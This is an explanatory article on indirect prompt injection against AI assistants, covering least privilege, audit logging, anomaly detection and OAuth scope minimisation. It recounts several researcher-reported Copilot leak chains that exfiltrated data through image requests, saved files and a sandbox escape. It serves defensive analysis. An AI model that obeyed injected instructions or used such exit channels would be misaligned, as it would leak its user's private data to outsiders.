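# Least privilege, audit logging and anomaly detection for AI assistants that read their users' files and history

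## How an assistant is hijacked, and the three controls that limit the harm

AI assistants such as Microsoft 365 Copilot and ChatGPT are language models connected to their user's data and to outside tools. They read the user's mail, files, calendar and notes from past conversations, and many can also send messages, create events and fetch web pages on the user's behalf. Much of what they read comes from other people. Anyone who knows the user's email address can put text in their mailbox, and if that text contains instructions, the assistant may follow them as though the user had given them. Security researchers call this technique indirect prompt injection. A hijack is a session in which the technique works and the assistant acts for an outsider.

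Developers train their models to resist such instructions, and in tests the best models of 2026 resist nearly all of them. Three older controls from computer security limit the harm from the rest. Least privilege limits what the assistant can read and do, audit logging keeps a lasting record of what it did, and anomaly detection flags unusual behaviour. All three are hard to apply because people want an assistant for its access to everything they have.

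### A summary of the landlord's messages

An assistant with a common set of connections can read its user's mail, files and calendar. It can also send mail, create calendar events and fetch web pages. In this example of a hijack, the user is a tenant who asks the assistant to summarise this week's messages from the landlord.

1. The program around the model assembles a prompt from the developer's standing instructions, a description of each tool, whatever the assistant has stored about the tenant, and the request.
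2. The model responds with a tool call, which is a structured request to an outside function. This one searches the mail for the landlord's name over the last seven days. The program runs the search with the tenant's own access rights.
3. The mail service returns the matching messages and the program adds their text to the prompt. An outsider wrote one of them. It matched because it mentions the landlord, and it contains instructions meant for the assistant.
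4. The model generates its next output from the whole prompt. If it follows the injected instructions, that output is a second tool call, for instance a search of the tenant's files for bank documents.
5. The program runs this call as well, because the call is well formed and the tenant's rights cover it. A third call sends the result out in an email, in the address of a web request or in an invitation to a shared calendar event. Any such route is an exit channel.
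6. The model writes the summary. The tenant reads it and may notice nothing.

The assistant routinely reads mail, files, history and stored memory, which together make up its trusted context. Some of that material comes from strangers, so the outsider could hijack the assistant without stealing a password or exploiting a bug in the mail service.

An ordinary program would have behaved differently at step 4. In SQL injection, an attack on databases that looks much the same, text that a visitor typed into a web form ran as a database command. Programmers fixed this with parameterised queries, which send the command and the visitor's text separately so that the database engine never interprets the text as a command. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), argues in the centre's article *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* (2025) that language models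 offer no place to put such a fix. A model predicts the next token, a word or fragment of a word, from all the text so far, and nothing inside it separates data from instructions. Developers can mark outside text as data or train the model to give their own instructions priority. Both methods make a hijack less likely, but neither gives the model a built-in separation between data and instructions. Filters for known phrases are less effective because an attacker can reword an instruction endlessly.

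The programmer Simon Willison coined the term "prompt injection". In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) explains that he named it after SQL injection because both mix trusted and untrusted text. David C agrees about the mechanism but thinks the comparison is dangerous, because it leads developers to expect a fix as complete as the one for SQL injection.

### The confused deputy

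Engineers called a program in the assistant's position a "confused deputy" long before language models. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the operating system let it write to any file there. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating system let the debugging output overwrite the billing records.

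The compiler was a deputy with authority from two sources, its own and its user's, and had no way to keep them apart. In the landlord case, the assistant is the deputy. The outsider has no right to open the tenant's files, but the assistant has that right and uses it on his behalf.

Hardy's remedy was the capability, a token that both names a file and grants the right to write to it. A user who wants debugging output written to a file must supply a capability for that file, and a user with no right to the billing file has no capability for it. The scheme works because the compiler writes its statistics at one point in its code and the debugging output at another, so a programmer can attach the proper authority to each. But an assistant's model produces every tool call by the same process from the same mixed text. David C therefore calls it an "inherently confusable deputy", meaning that its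 flaw, unlike the compiler's, may have no repair.

### What theft requires

Willison names three conditions that together let an outsider steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. The landlord assistant meets all three in normal use, because it reads the tenant's files, reads mail from anyone, and can send mail.

Removing any one of the conditions would prevent the theft. The exit channel looks like the easiest to remove, since an assistant can write a summary without sending mail, but it is hard to identify every exit. When an assistant fetches a web page, the address it requests can carry stolen text to whoever runs the site. Willison points out that loading an image, or showing a link that the user then clicks, can also send text out. He lists more than a dozen products in which researchers demonstrated this kind of theft after April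 2023, including Microsoft 365 Copilot, whose leaks continued into 2026. The vendors fixed almost all of these flaws promptly, usually by closing the particular exit involved.

That repair depends on one company controlling the whole product. Many users combine tools from different makers through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting tools to models, so no single vendor can see or close every route. A single tool can also be enough to leak private data. GitHub's official connector could read both public issue reports, which anyone may file, and private code repositories, and it could open pull requests (proposed code changes) that exposed what it had read.

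Willison's conditions cover only data theft. A hijacked assistant can also delete mail or add a fake appointment, which requires neither secret data nor a way to send data out. Similarly, Tymshare lost its billing records without anyone reading them.

### How often injections still succeed

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, dated 24 July, is among the most detailed recent sources. (A system card is the report on testing that a developer publishes with a model.) The test behind its main injection figures, as the Japanese technology site TechFeed describes it, came from Anthropic together with the security firm Gray Swan, the UK AI Security Institute and the US Center for AI Standards and Innovation. It covers 28 scenarios in coding, tool use and control of a screen, and draws on 1,130 attacks of a general kind. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting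 Prompt Injection* (2026) quotes the chance that an attacker succeeds within 15 attempts:

| Model | Developer | Success within 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | Anthropic | 2.0% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | Anthropic | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Anthropic | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | Anthropic | 5.9% |
| Muse Spark | Meta | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | OpenAI | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | OpenAI | 20.8% |

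Against Opus 5, a single attempt succeeded 0.2% of the time. If attempts were independent, at least one of 15 would succeed about 3% of the time. The measured rate was 2.0%, which suggests that a few combinations of attack and scenario work repeatedly while most never work. An attacker who finds one that works can reuse it, and email is nearly free to send. If the 2.0% rate carried over to real mailboxes, which nobody has shown, someone who made 15 attempts on each of 10,000 users would hijack the assistants of about 200.

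How often injections succeed depends on the setting as much as the model. In February 2026, VentureBeat reported from Anthropic's figures that injections against Claude Opus 4.6 failed in all 200 attempts in a constrained coding environment. When the same model operated a graphical interface with extended thinking, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards. By the 200th attempt the figure had reached 78.6%, and safeguards reduced that only to 57.1%. Later results are far better. VentureBeat reported from the May system card that injections against Claude Opus 4.8, working as a browser agent with thinking on, succeeded in 31.5% of attempts without safeguards and 0.5% with them.

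The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* (2026) reported that the browser figure fell to zero across 129 test scenarios for Opus 5. That is a strong result, but the sample is small. Even if the scenarios were a random sample of what attackers try, the result would be consistent with a true failure rate of up to about 2.3% per scenario at the 95% confidence level. Attackers also look for scenarios that the developer left out. In September, Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5 reported performance similar to or better than Opus 5's on every injection test it included.

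All of these figures come from a developer's own publication. Gray Swan has since begun to publish results for many developers' models in its *Frontier Hazard Tracker*. Its researchers write the tests themselves and keep the items private so that they stay out of training data. According to iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* (2026), Google's Gemini 4 Argon did best: attackers succeeded 2.3% of the time within 15 attacks. Anthropic's models came close behind. Nvidia's Nemotron 3.5 Super VL, whose weights anyone can download and run, failed 94.3% of the time. An assistant's exposure therefore depends heavily on which model its maker chose, and even with the best model, a few in every hundred persistent attackers succeed.

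### AgentDojo

Researchers often test defences for assistants on AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates office work, banking, travel booking and workplace chat. Each test gives the assistant a user's task and simulated tools, and plants an injection in a tool's output. An attack succeeds if the assistant carries out the planted goal, for example if a payment to the attacker appears in the simulated bank account. The benchmark also scores whether the assistant finished the user's own task, and a defence should be judged on both scores. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026) describes a test by researchers at the University of Waterloo, Zhejiang University and KTH Royal Institute of Technology. PromptGuard, a filter that discards any document it flags, blocked slightly more attacks than the researchers' own method, but the assistant completed only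 16.19% of its users' tasks because the discarded documents held the data it needed.

Low attack success rates on AgentDojo can mislead when the attacks are old. The same team retrained two small models to check, before each action, whether the action served the user's request. Off-the-shelf injections then succeeded on AgentDojo in less than half a percent of attempts. Attackers who rewrote their injections over about 250 tries succeeded on up to 10% of 40 tasks that the researchers had picked as known weak spots. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) reports that the company's latest models have already saturated the commonly used robustness tests. On a saturated test, an undefended model scores almost as well as a defended one, so it is hard to see how much an added control helps.

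A real mailbox differs from AgentDojo's in ways that matter for all three controls. It holds years of correspondence, and the test's designers don't know its owner's habits. AgentDojo plants injections on purpose, so its results don't measure how rare they are in ordinary mail. It also runs each task as a separate session, whereas an injection in stored memory can take effect weeks later. Chu (2026) reviewed 116 papers in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* and found no benchmark that tests attacks whose effects build up across sessions.

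### Before, during and after

In his advice for the NCSC, David C says security teams should treat prompt injection as a risk that remains even with every product and filter in place, and should assume that, at worst, an attacker gains control of the assistant's tools. He recommends safeguards that limit what the system can do and do not themselves rely on a language model. If an organisation cannot tolerate the remaining risk, he suggests that the task may not suit a language model.

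One rule, from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that a model reading someone's text should have only that person's privileges. Applied strictly, the rule would let the assistant summarise the landlord's messages but not check a claim about the rent against the lease in the tenant's files, because the landlord has no right to open those files. The rule protects the tenant, but it also prevents much of what they wanted the assistant to do.

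The general principle behind it, which Saltzer and Schroeder set out in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), is that every program and every user should operate with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". They argued that this limits the damage a program can do when it fails and leaves fewer programs to examine when someone investigates a misuse. Least privilege acts before the harm, because someone sets the limits before the session runs. For the landlord summary, the assistant needs only read access to one correspondent's messages from one week. With only that access, the search for bank documents at step 4 fails, and so does any attempt to send the results.

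Least privilege is hard to apply to an assistant for two reasons. Saltzer and Schroeder had in mind programs with a known job, but an assistant gets a new job with each request, and the user's next one may be to find a lease and email it to an insurer. They also wanted the system to check every access for authority, which they noted requires a foolproof way to identify the source of each request. The program that runs the assistant's tool calls can identify the assistant as their source, but not whose text prompted them.

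Reviewing permissions one at a time can also miss the danger. In *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI*, Parisel (2026) argues that permissions which look harmless separately can become dangerous when agents combine them. The paper is theoretical, deals mainly with groups of agents in large organisations, and reports no trial. The same problem can arise with a single assistant, because reading files, reading mail and sending mail are all routine permissions that together meet Willison's three conditions.

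Audit logging helps only after the harm is done. Saltzer and Schroeder described an early form, compromise recording, and compared it to an unbreakable padlock on a flimsy file cabinet. A thief can still get at the papers, but the broken cabinet will show that he did. They thought it of limited use in computers, where a clever intruder can erase the traces. For assistants, the Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre, a government body whose guidance recommends all three controls, advises organisations to log prompts, tool calls, approvals and the data sources the assistant accessed. The tenant could use such a log to learn which bank documents left and where they went, but not to recover them.

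Anomaly detection is the only one of the three controls that can act while the harm is happening, and only if the detector runs before the call that sends the data. The detector compares the trace, the ordered record of tool calls and results in a session, with a model of normal behaviour. David C recommends that designers work out in advance what normal use looks like, and suggests watching for failed tool calls, since an attacker will probably need several tries to refine an attack. In the landlord session, a search of the bank documents followed by an email to a new address should stand out because the request was for a summary. A mortgage application is harder to judge, because the tenant will send the same documents to an address the assistant has never seen. Because real hijacks are rare, even a low rate of false alarms can make them hard to find among the alerts.

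## Microsoft 365 Copilot: repeated data leaks, 2025 to 2026

Microsoft 365 Copilot is an assistant that runs in Word, Excel, Outlook and Teams. In June 2025 researchers at Aim Labs showed that one email from a stranger could make it leak a company's data, an attack they called EchoLeak. A year later the security company Varonis published a second attack, SearchLeak. In December 2026 the team behind EchoLeak, by then called Cato AI Labs, published three more under the name ReLeak.

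All five leaks were demonstrations by researchers at companies that sell security products. Microsoft has fixed the flaws, and none of the companies reports a theft by a real attacker. The sequence is useful because the product and its access to user data stayed much the same while the ways to get data out changed.

### How Copilot answers a question

Suppose an employee asks Copilot what budget her team agreed for a project. The language model was never trained on her company's files, so Copilot looks the answer up first, a method called retrieval-augmented generation. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, describes how it works:

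1. Copilot queries Microsoft Graph, the service that gives programs access to an organisation's Microsoft 365 data.
2. Graph returns whatever looks relevant from her mailbox, her OneDrive storage, Office files, internal SharePoint sites and Teams chats.
3. Copilot adds this material to the model's context, the text from which the model generates its answer. The context also holds her question and the conversation so far.
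4. The model writes an answer and her browser displays it, including any links and images.

Copilot inherits the employee's permissions, so step 2 returns only items that she could open herself. Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot* quotes Aim Labs' caution that those items may still include sensitive or proprietary information. The permission check keeps Copilot from retrieving colleagues' files that she can't open, but it doesn't filter items by who wrote them. She may open her own mail, so an email from a stranger passes the check and enters the same context as the budget.

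The budget question needs perhaps one spreadsheet and one chat thread, but the search covers everything she has permission to open. Old conversations can add to the problem. For example, TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot* describes CoSnitch, a Copilot flaw that let outsiders plant instructions in stored memory.

### EchoLeak: an email and a Teams relay

Anyone could start the EchoLeak attack by sending an email, and the recipient did not have to open it. The email stayed in the mailbox until the recipient asked Copilot a question that seemed related, and Copilot then retrieved it along with the company's own material. The researchers found that a single email could match questions on various topics, but Ravia gives no figure for how often Copilot retrieved it or how often the whole attack worked.

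Once the email was in the context, its instructions made the model select sensitive information and put it in the address of an image. Browsers load images automatically, so displaying the answer sent the request, with the information in it. Microsoft had several defences against this, and the researchers got past all of them. Reddy and Gujral (2025) trace the same steps in their case study, *EchoLeak*.

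The first defence, a classifier that screened incoming text for injections, let the email through. Ravia explains that such classifiers are hard to train because good collections of real injections are scarce. A second defence removed outside links from Copilot's answers, but it did not recognise every link format.

The third was the web page's content security policy, a list of addresses from which the browser may load images. The policy would have blocked a request sent straight to the researchers' server, so the researchers looked for an approved service that would pass the request on. SharePoint could do this, but only if the user first accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Then they found a Teams service that would fetch an outside address with no action from the user. The browser contacted Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams requested an address on the researchers' server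 that contained the stolen text.

The policy therefore controlled only the first request. It could not control what an approved service did next.

РБК-Україна's *Помилка Microsoft змусила Copilot довіряти хакерам*, which draws on reporting by Ars Technica, notes that one of Copilot's safeguards stops it from sending email or filling in web forms on its own. That limit is sensible, but data could still leave through image loading. A rule that covers only the assistant's tool calls misses data that leaves when the browser displays the answer.

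Text from outside the organisation caused the model to use data from inside it, as in Hardy's confused deputy. Ravia calls this fault an "LLM scope violation" and holds that an outsider's email should never be able to cause the model to use internal data. Like the rule from Willison's exchange with Bista, this restriction would also prevent useful work, such as checking a supplier's quotation against the signed contract.

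Aim Labs reported EchoLeak to Microsoft in January 2025, and Microsoft finished the fix in May. The public report followed on 11 June. Ravia writes that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected. The Next Web reports that the flaw scored 9.3 out of 10 for severity on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS).

### Bing as an exit, twice

*SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes a one-click attack on Copilot Enterprise Search, the part of Copilot that searches company data. The victim received a link to a genuine Microsoft address that contained a search query. Copilot treated the query as instructions and ran them as soon as the page opened.

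SearchLeak exposed more data than EchoLeak, which Ravia describes as the theft of whatever was in the conversation's context. In SearchLeak, the outsider's instructions could start new searches across the victim's mail, calendar, SharePoint sites and OneDrive files. Taler's demonstration took only the subject line of an email, but a subject line can contain a login code that might let an attacker into another account.

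The attack again used an image to extract the data. Microsoft had a safeguard that turned any formatting in Copilot's answer into plain text, but it ran only when the answer was complete. Copilot shows its answers as the model generates them, so by then the browser had already requested the image. The content security policy allowed images from Bing, Microsoft's search engine, and Bing has a feature that fetches an image from any address it receives. Bing's servers made the request that carried the data out.

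Ravia's report had printed that policy's approved list a year earlier, and it already included Bing and more than two dozen other addresses. Taler advises security teams to review any approved service that fetches addresses supplied by users. However, Microsoft writes the policy for Copilot's own page, so a customer could examine the list but would have to wait for Microsoft to change it.

Microsoft fixed SearchLeak on 4 June 2026, according to Security.NL's *Microsoft 365 Copilot-lek maakte via één click diefstal e-mails mogelijk*, and customers did not need to install anything. Varonis published the details on 15 June. Taler does not say when Microsoft received the report and mentions no use of the flaw by real attackers.

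Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* (2026) reports that Microsoft scored the flaw's severity at 6.5, or medium, because the victim had to click. The US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, or high, because it judged that the attack needed no user interaction. Taler's account supports Microsoft on that point, since nothing happened until the victim opened the link. Yet he also writes that Microsoft labelled the flaw "critical", its highest severity rating. Both can be true, because Microsoft assigns the label separately from the score. An administrator who sorted flaws by score alone could have ranked this one low, even though it exposed everything an employee could open.

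The first ReLeak chain also used Bing, but this time the user didn't have to click anything. Simonovich published the three chains for Cato AI Labs on 3 December in *ReLeak* (2026). Antipov's *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (2026) gives a detailed account for the Russian site SecurityLab. As in EchoLeak, the attack began with an email that Copilot retrieved while handling an ordinary request. According to Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026), the email could stay unread in the inbox throughout. Copilot put private data in the address of an image, the browser loaded the image through Bing, and Bing passed the data to an outside server.

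Cato reported its three chains between 29 July and 20 August, so researchers again had a way to send data out through Bing at most eleven weeks after the SearchLeak fix. One possible explanation, based on Taler's description, is that Microsoft fixed the handling of links or the late safeguard and left Bing's fetching alone. SearchLeak needed three separate weaknesses, so fixing any one would have stopped it, but the route through Bing would have remained open to the next attack. Neither Taler nor Antipov says which part Microsoft changed.

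### A saved file and a code sandbox

The other two ReLeak chains used newer features that let Copilot create files and run programs, and did not depend on how the browser displayed an answer. Antipov notes that such features have increased the number of ways data can leak out.

In one attack chain, Copilot created a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF document and saved it to OneDrive or SharePoint. The data left through a link in the saved file, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026). Microsoft's servers process saved files in the background, and in Cato's tests that processing sent private data out between one and eight minutes after the conversation ended, without anyone having to open the document.

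The delay also matters for the other controls, because a detector that judged only the conversation would have had to flag a saved file, which office assistants routinely produce. The data left later, from a different system, and would have left even if the employee had already closed the chat and shut down her computer.

The last chain broke out of Copilot's code interpreter. When a task needs calculation, such as making a chart from a spreadsheet, Copilot writes a short program and runs it in a sandbox, an isolated machine. Microsoft states in its documentation that these machines allow no inbound or outbound traffic and that this prevents data theft. It also describes using a fresh machine for each run and scanning for malicious code in real time. Cato's researchers still got the sandbox to send data directly to an outside server. Antipov reports a CVSS score of 8.6 for this flaw, raised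 from an initial 7.4, but could not confirm any public scores for the other two.

*Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate* (Lahav, 2026) had already described another escape from Copilot's code sandbox. A document that the user gave Copilot opened a channel through which researchers at the data-security company Rubrik could question that user's Copilot and read its answers. HeadTopics' *RubrikがMicrosoft 365 Copilotの脆弱性と攻撃手法ChatMateを公開* reports that the sandbox had no internet connection but the machine running it did, and that Microsoft fixed the flaw in April 2026 after receiving a report in February.

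Microsoft repaired one failure of the sandbox in April and received a report of another by late August. A sandbox with no network access is still one of the strongest limits available, because it works even if an outsider has completely hijacked the model. But it protects data only if the isolation works as documented, and customers have few ways to check that.

Microsoft released fixes for the ReLeak chains on 17 September, 11 November and 15 November. The published accounts do not match each date to a chain. Cato had reported all three chains to Microsoft by 20 August, so at least two stayed unfixed for 83 days or more. Cato said on 3 December that it knew of no affected customers and no real attacks. That is weaker evidence than a search of Microsoft's own records would give, because Cato can only report cases it has heard about.

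Cato's researchers directed AI agents that helped find the flaws by writing test cases, analysing Copilot's refusals and adjusting the next attempt. If attackers can do the same, they are more likely to find a flaw in the months between its report and its fix.

### The five chains compared

For each attack, the last column of the table gives a limit on access that would have stopped it. These limits follow from what each attack needed, and the researchers did not test them.

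| Chain | What the user had to do | Data in reach | Exit channel | Report to Microsoft | Fix | Known real use | Access limit that would cut the chain |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Ask Copilot an ordinary question | Everything in the conversation's context, including retrieved mail and files | Image request through a Teams service | January 2025 | May 2025 | None, according to Microsoft | No internal data in a context that holds an outsider's email |
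| SearchLeak | Click one link | Mail, calendar and files that the user may open | Image request through Bing | No published date | 4 June 2026 | None reported | No search of private data until the user submits the query herself |
| ReLeak: image | Ask Copilot an ordinary question | Private data within the user's permissions | Image request through Bing | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 17 September, 11 November or 15 November 2026 | None known to Cato | No images from services that fetch outside addresses |
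| ReLeak: saved file | Ask Copilot an ordinary question | Private data within the user's permissions | Background fetching by Microsoft's servers | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 17 September, 11 November or 15 November 2026 | None known to Cato | No outside requests during the processing of files that Copilot creates |
| ReLeak: code | Ask Copilot an ordinary question | Private data within the user's permissions | Direct transfer from the code sandbox | 29 July to 20 August 2026 | 17 September, 11 November or 15 November 2026 | None known to Cato | No code execution in a session that has read an outsider's email |

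The limit in the EchoLeak row would also have stopped all three ReLeak chains, because each began with an outsider's email in the same context as private data. It would not have stopped SearchLeak, where the instructions arrived in a link. The limits on images and background requests would inconvenience users less, but each blocks only one way of sending data out.

### Could an administrator have prevented EchoLeak?

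Ravia writes that, to the best of Aim Labs' knowledge, "no admin configuration or user behavior could have prevented the exploitation". Aim Security had a commercial reason to think so, because the same report advertises the company's guardrails as protection, and these are easier to sell if customers' existing settings cannot help. Checking which parts of the attack chain an administrator controlled would test the claim.

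The email could come from any address, so a list of blocked senders would not have stopped it. An administrator could have refused all mail from outside the company, but that would have cut off customers and suppliers. The classifier and the link filter, which Microsoft ran, both failed.

A company firewall would have done little to stop the data from leaving. The employee's browser connected to Teams, which her company used all day, and Microsoft's network made the connection to the attacker's server. To block the leak, the company would have had to inspect encrypted traffic and single out one function of Teams, which it had no reason to suspect before Aim Labs found the flaw.

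Administrators had some control over what Copilot could read. They could remove an employee's access to files she did not need, which would also have removed Copilot's access. SharePoint's restricted search setting, which Microsoft introduced in 2024, also let them limit organisation-wide search and Copilot to a list of approved sites. Either measure would have reduced what EchoLeak could take but would not have prevented the attack, because the employee's own mail and the conversation itself would still have been accessible.

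Aim Labs' statement therefore holds for a company that received outside mail and kept Copilot running. But it covers only whether the attack could succeed, and an administrator also cares about how much data the attacker gets. Hijacking the Copilot of an employee with access to four shared folders exposes far less than hijacking that of an employee with access to four thousand, even if the attack works equally well on both.

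### What administrators can restrict, and what it costs

The restrictions open to administrators differ widely in how much usefulness they cost.

Removing permissions that employees don't use is the least disruptive measure. Copilot can no longer find the files those permissions covered, and although employees lose access too, they presumably didn't need it. Someone has to decide which permissions are unused, and do so again as people change jobs. Removing them also does little to protect a finance director, who needs broad access and whose mailbox an attacker would most like to read.

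Restricted SharePoint search limits Copilot further by stopping it from answering from shared sites that are not on the list, even though one of them may hold the best answer. At launch the list could hold 100 sites, which is few for a large organisation. The setting still lets Copilot read personal mail, so it would not have stopped Varonis from taking the subject line in its demonstration.

Administrators can also use Purview, Microsoft's data-protection product, to stop Copilot from using the contents of files that carry a chosen sensitivity label. Employees then have to read and summarise those files themselves, and these may well be the long contracts and financial plans they wanted help with. Microsoft says the code interpreter cannot read files with data protections either, so Copilot cannot use it to chart the figures in a protected spreadsheet. Labels help only where someone has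 applied them, and an email containing a login code will usually have none.

Turning off Copilot's web search probably would not have closed the Bing exits. The employee's browser requested the image while displaying the answer, which did not require Copilot to search the web. With web search off, she would lose current information from the web and still be exposed to the same kind of leak.

Varonis recommends monitoring for Copilot search links that contain hidden instructions. This takes the security team's time but doesn't restrict Copilot's functions. It would more likely help the team find out who had clicked than stop the first theft, since the data left within moments of the page opening. Taler also asks users to inspect links before they click, but these links led to a real Microsoft address, which employees learn to treat as a sign of safety.

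The restriction best suited to EchoLeak and ReLeak is to keep outsiders' email out of Copilot's context. An organisation could in principle label all mail from outside and exclude that label, provided the exclusion took effect before the model read the text. Neither Ravia nor Antipov reports testing this. It would make Copilot much less useful to anyone who deals with the public. A sales manager, for example, could no longer ask Copilot what a customer wanted. An organisation could apply the rule only to staff who handle its most sensitive data and rarely write to outsiders, and leave Copilot's access to everyone else's mail unchanged.

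## OAuth scopes and AirGapAgent: limiting what an assistant may read

Copilot can read an employee's mail because Microsoft runs both the assistant and the mailbox. An assistant from another company has to ask for access, usually through OAuth, an open standard that lets one service use an account at another without being given the password. The user approves a list of permissions, and this is the first chance to apply least privilege.

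### Consent, scope and token

Suppose the tenant connects an assistant to their Gmail account. Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025), in *MiniScope*, describe how such a connection works:

1. The assistant's program sends the tenant to Google's login page and names the scopes it wants. A scope is a permission that covers a fixed set of operations, such as reading mail or changing calendar events.
2. The tenant signs in and consents.
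3. Google issues the program an access token, a temporary credential that carries the approved scopes.
4. The program attaches the token to each request it makes for the tenant, and Google carries out any request that the scopes cover.

Most such tokens are bearer tokens, which work for whoever holds them. Sharma, Jiang and colleagues (2026) point out in *Beyond OAuth* that a server cannot tell one permitted use of a token from another. An injected search of the mailbox looks the same to Google as the tenant's own search.

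Users grant permissions when they connect an account, before they have asked the assistant to do anything, so the developer has to request scopes for every task they are likely to want. An assistant that summarises mail and also sends replies needs permission to read and to send, and it keeps both even when the user wants only a summary. Zhu and colleagues found that ChatGPT and Claude worked this way with personal services such as Gmail and Slack. Users approved a preset list of permissions once, and later tool calls went ahead without further confirmation.

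Scopes are also coarse, because they name operations without the details. Sharma and colleagues give the example of a user who wants to send $100 to Bob. The bank can ask only whether the assistant may make transfers, and approval covers any amount to any recipient. Similarly, a scope for reading messages does not specify a sender or time period. The landlord summary needs only a few messages, but the scope usually gives access to the whole mailbox, including years of letters from doctors, employers and banks.

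A mail service could offer narrower scopes, such as one for each correspondent, but the tenant would then need a new grant whenever a task involved someone else. Sharma and colleagues argue that finer scopes cannot solve the general problem, because the possible combinations multiply and some details emerge only while the task runs. Their alternative, PAUTH, derives permission from the wording of each task.

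### MiniScope: computing the smallest set of scopes

Even with coarse scopes, developers can avoid asking for more than their product uses. Zhu and colleagues compared the permissions that ChatGPT's and Claude's connectors requested with the minimum needed for their advertised functions. The table shows how many operations each set of permissions allowed in late 2025.

| Service | ChatGPT requested | ChatGPT needed | Claude requested | Claude needed |
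|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gmail | 50 | 32 | 32 | 32 |
| Google Calendar | 12 | 5 | 15 | 15 |
| Google file storage | 27 | 27 | 45 | 27 |
| Notion | 32 | 13 | 32 | 29 |
| Dropbox | 44 | 25 | not compared | not compared |

Six of the nine connectors requested more permissions than they needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector offered only features for reading mail, but its permissions also allowed it to change and delete mail. A hijacked assistant could have used these extra permissions if its own tool restrictions had a flaw. Removing them would have protected the tenant's mail from deletion, but the connector could still have read every message.

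MiniScope, the system by Zhu and colleagues, goes further and works out permissions for each request. The assistant starts with no access. When the user asks for something, the model writes a plan of its calls, and MiniScope computes the smallest set of scopes that covers the plan.

MiniScope builds a hierarchy of scopes from the service's public documentation, which lists the scopes that permit each operation. If scope B allows everything that scope A allows, MiniScope places A below B. The hierarchy matters because many operations have several possible scopes, including 24 of the 37 operations in Google Calendar.

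MiniScope then solves an integer program, an optimisation problem in which each variable here is 0 or 1. Let x(s) be 1 if scope s is in the chosen set and 0 if it is not, and let c(s) be the number of operations that s allows. The program finds the values that

minimise Σ c(s) · x(s), on condition that every call in the plan has at least one chosen scope that permits it.

Choosing the narrowest scope for each call separately can grant more access than choosing scopes for the whole plan. Suppose a plan has two calls. Scope P allows the first call and two other operations, scope Q allows the second call and three others, and scope R allows both calls and three others. P is the narrowest scope for the first call and Q for the second, but together they allow seven operations. R allows only five, so MiniScope requests R.

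The user can approve the request once, for the session or permanently, or refuse it. A separate component checks every tool call against what the user approved and holds the real credentials, so the model never handles them. In the landlord example, the tenant approves reading mail for the session. The injected search of their files needs another scope, so MiniScope stops the call and asks the tenant for permission. A tenant who wanted a summary of some messages has a fair chance of noticing that something is wrong, but no prompt appears if they have already chosen "always allow" for files.

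If the injected instruction is to search for the bank's emails instead, MiniScope allows the search because it falls within the scope the tenant has just approved, a limit that Zhu and colleagues acknowledge. MiniScope also would not have stopped the image requests in three of the five Copilot chains, because loading an image needs no scope.

MiniScope's computation adds 1 to 6% to the running time. When language models did the same job, they granted more access than MiniScope. GPT 5's choices allowed 3 to 12% more operations on average, and those of Qwen 3, an open model, up to 119% more. The larger burden is on the user, who has to answer questions. In a simulation of three months of Gmail requests, between 18% and 60% of requests led to a question, depending on how cautious the simulated user was. These users were rules or language models, so the simulation is weak evidence of how carefully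 a real person would read each question after answering dozens of them.

### When no grant is the smallest

MiniScope chose R in the example above because five is less than seven. R allows three operations that P and Q don't, and P and Q allow five that R doesn't. If one of R's three extra operations deletes a calendar, the tenant might well prefer P and Q.

Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, measured how often this problem arises in the permissions that Google and Microsoft publish. Xu calls one grant smaller than another only if the larger one allows everything the smaller one does and more. A grant is minimal for a task if it is sufficient and no smaller grant is. A task can have several minimal grants, each allowing something the others don't, so none of them is the smallest.

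The Microsoft data came from Graph, the service that Copilot searches, and contained 22,305 bindings between permissions and operations. The Google data covered 23,852 methods, Google's term for operations, across 517 services. The measurements come directly from the companies' own tables and did not involve a language model.

Xu also generated the tasks from the tables, by grouping operations that act on the same kind of resource. On Graph, 29.8% and 30.7% of tasks had no single smallest grant under the two main types of access, which covered 493 and 450 tasks. The share was 33.3% for personal accounts, but that figure rests on only 24 tasks. On Google it was 3.2% of 2,822 tasks, which Xu attributes to Google's more finely divided scopes. Nobody observed these tasks in use, so an assistant whose users mostly ask for mail summaries could meet the problem far less often than these rates suggest,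 or far more often if its common tasks happen to be ones with no single smallest grant.

One of the Google cases involves BigQuery, the company's data-analysis service. Two minimal grants allow an assistant to read a project's metadata:

- The `bigquery` scope allows 286 operations across 10 services, of which 144 change something.
- The `cloud-platform.read-only` scope allows 565 operations across 27 services, of which 61 change something.

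The 61 look odd in a read-only scope, but some may be harmless because Xu inferred changes mainly from the type of web request.

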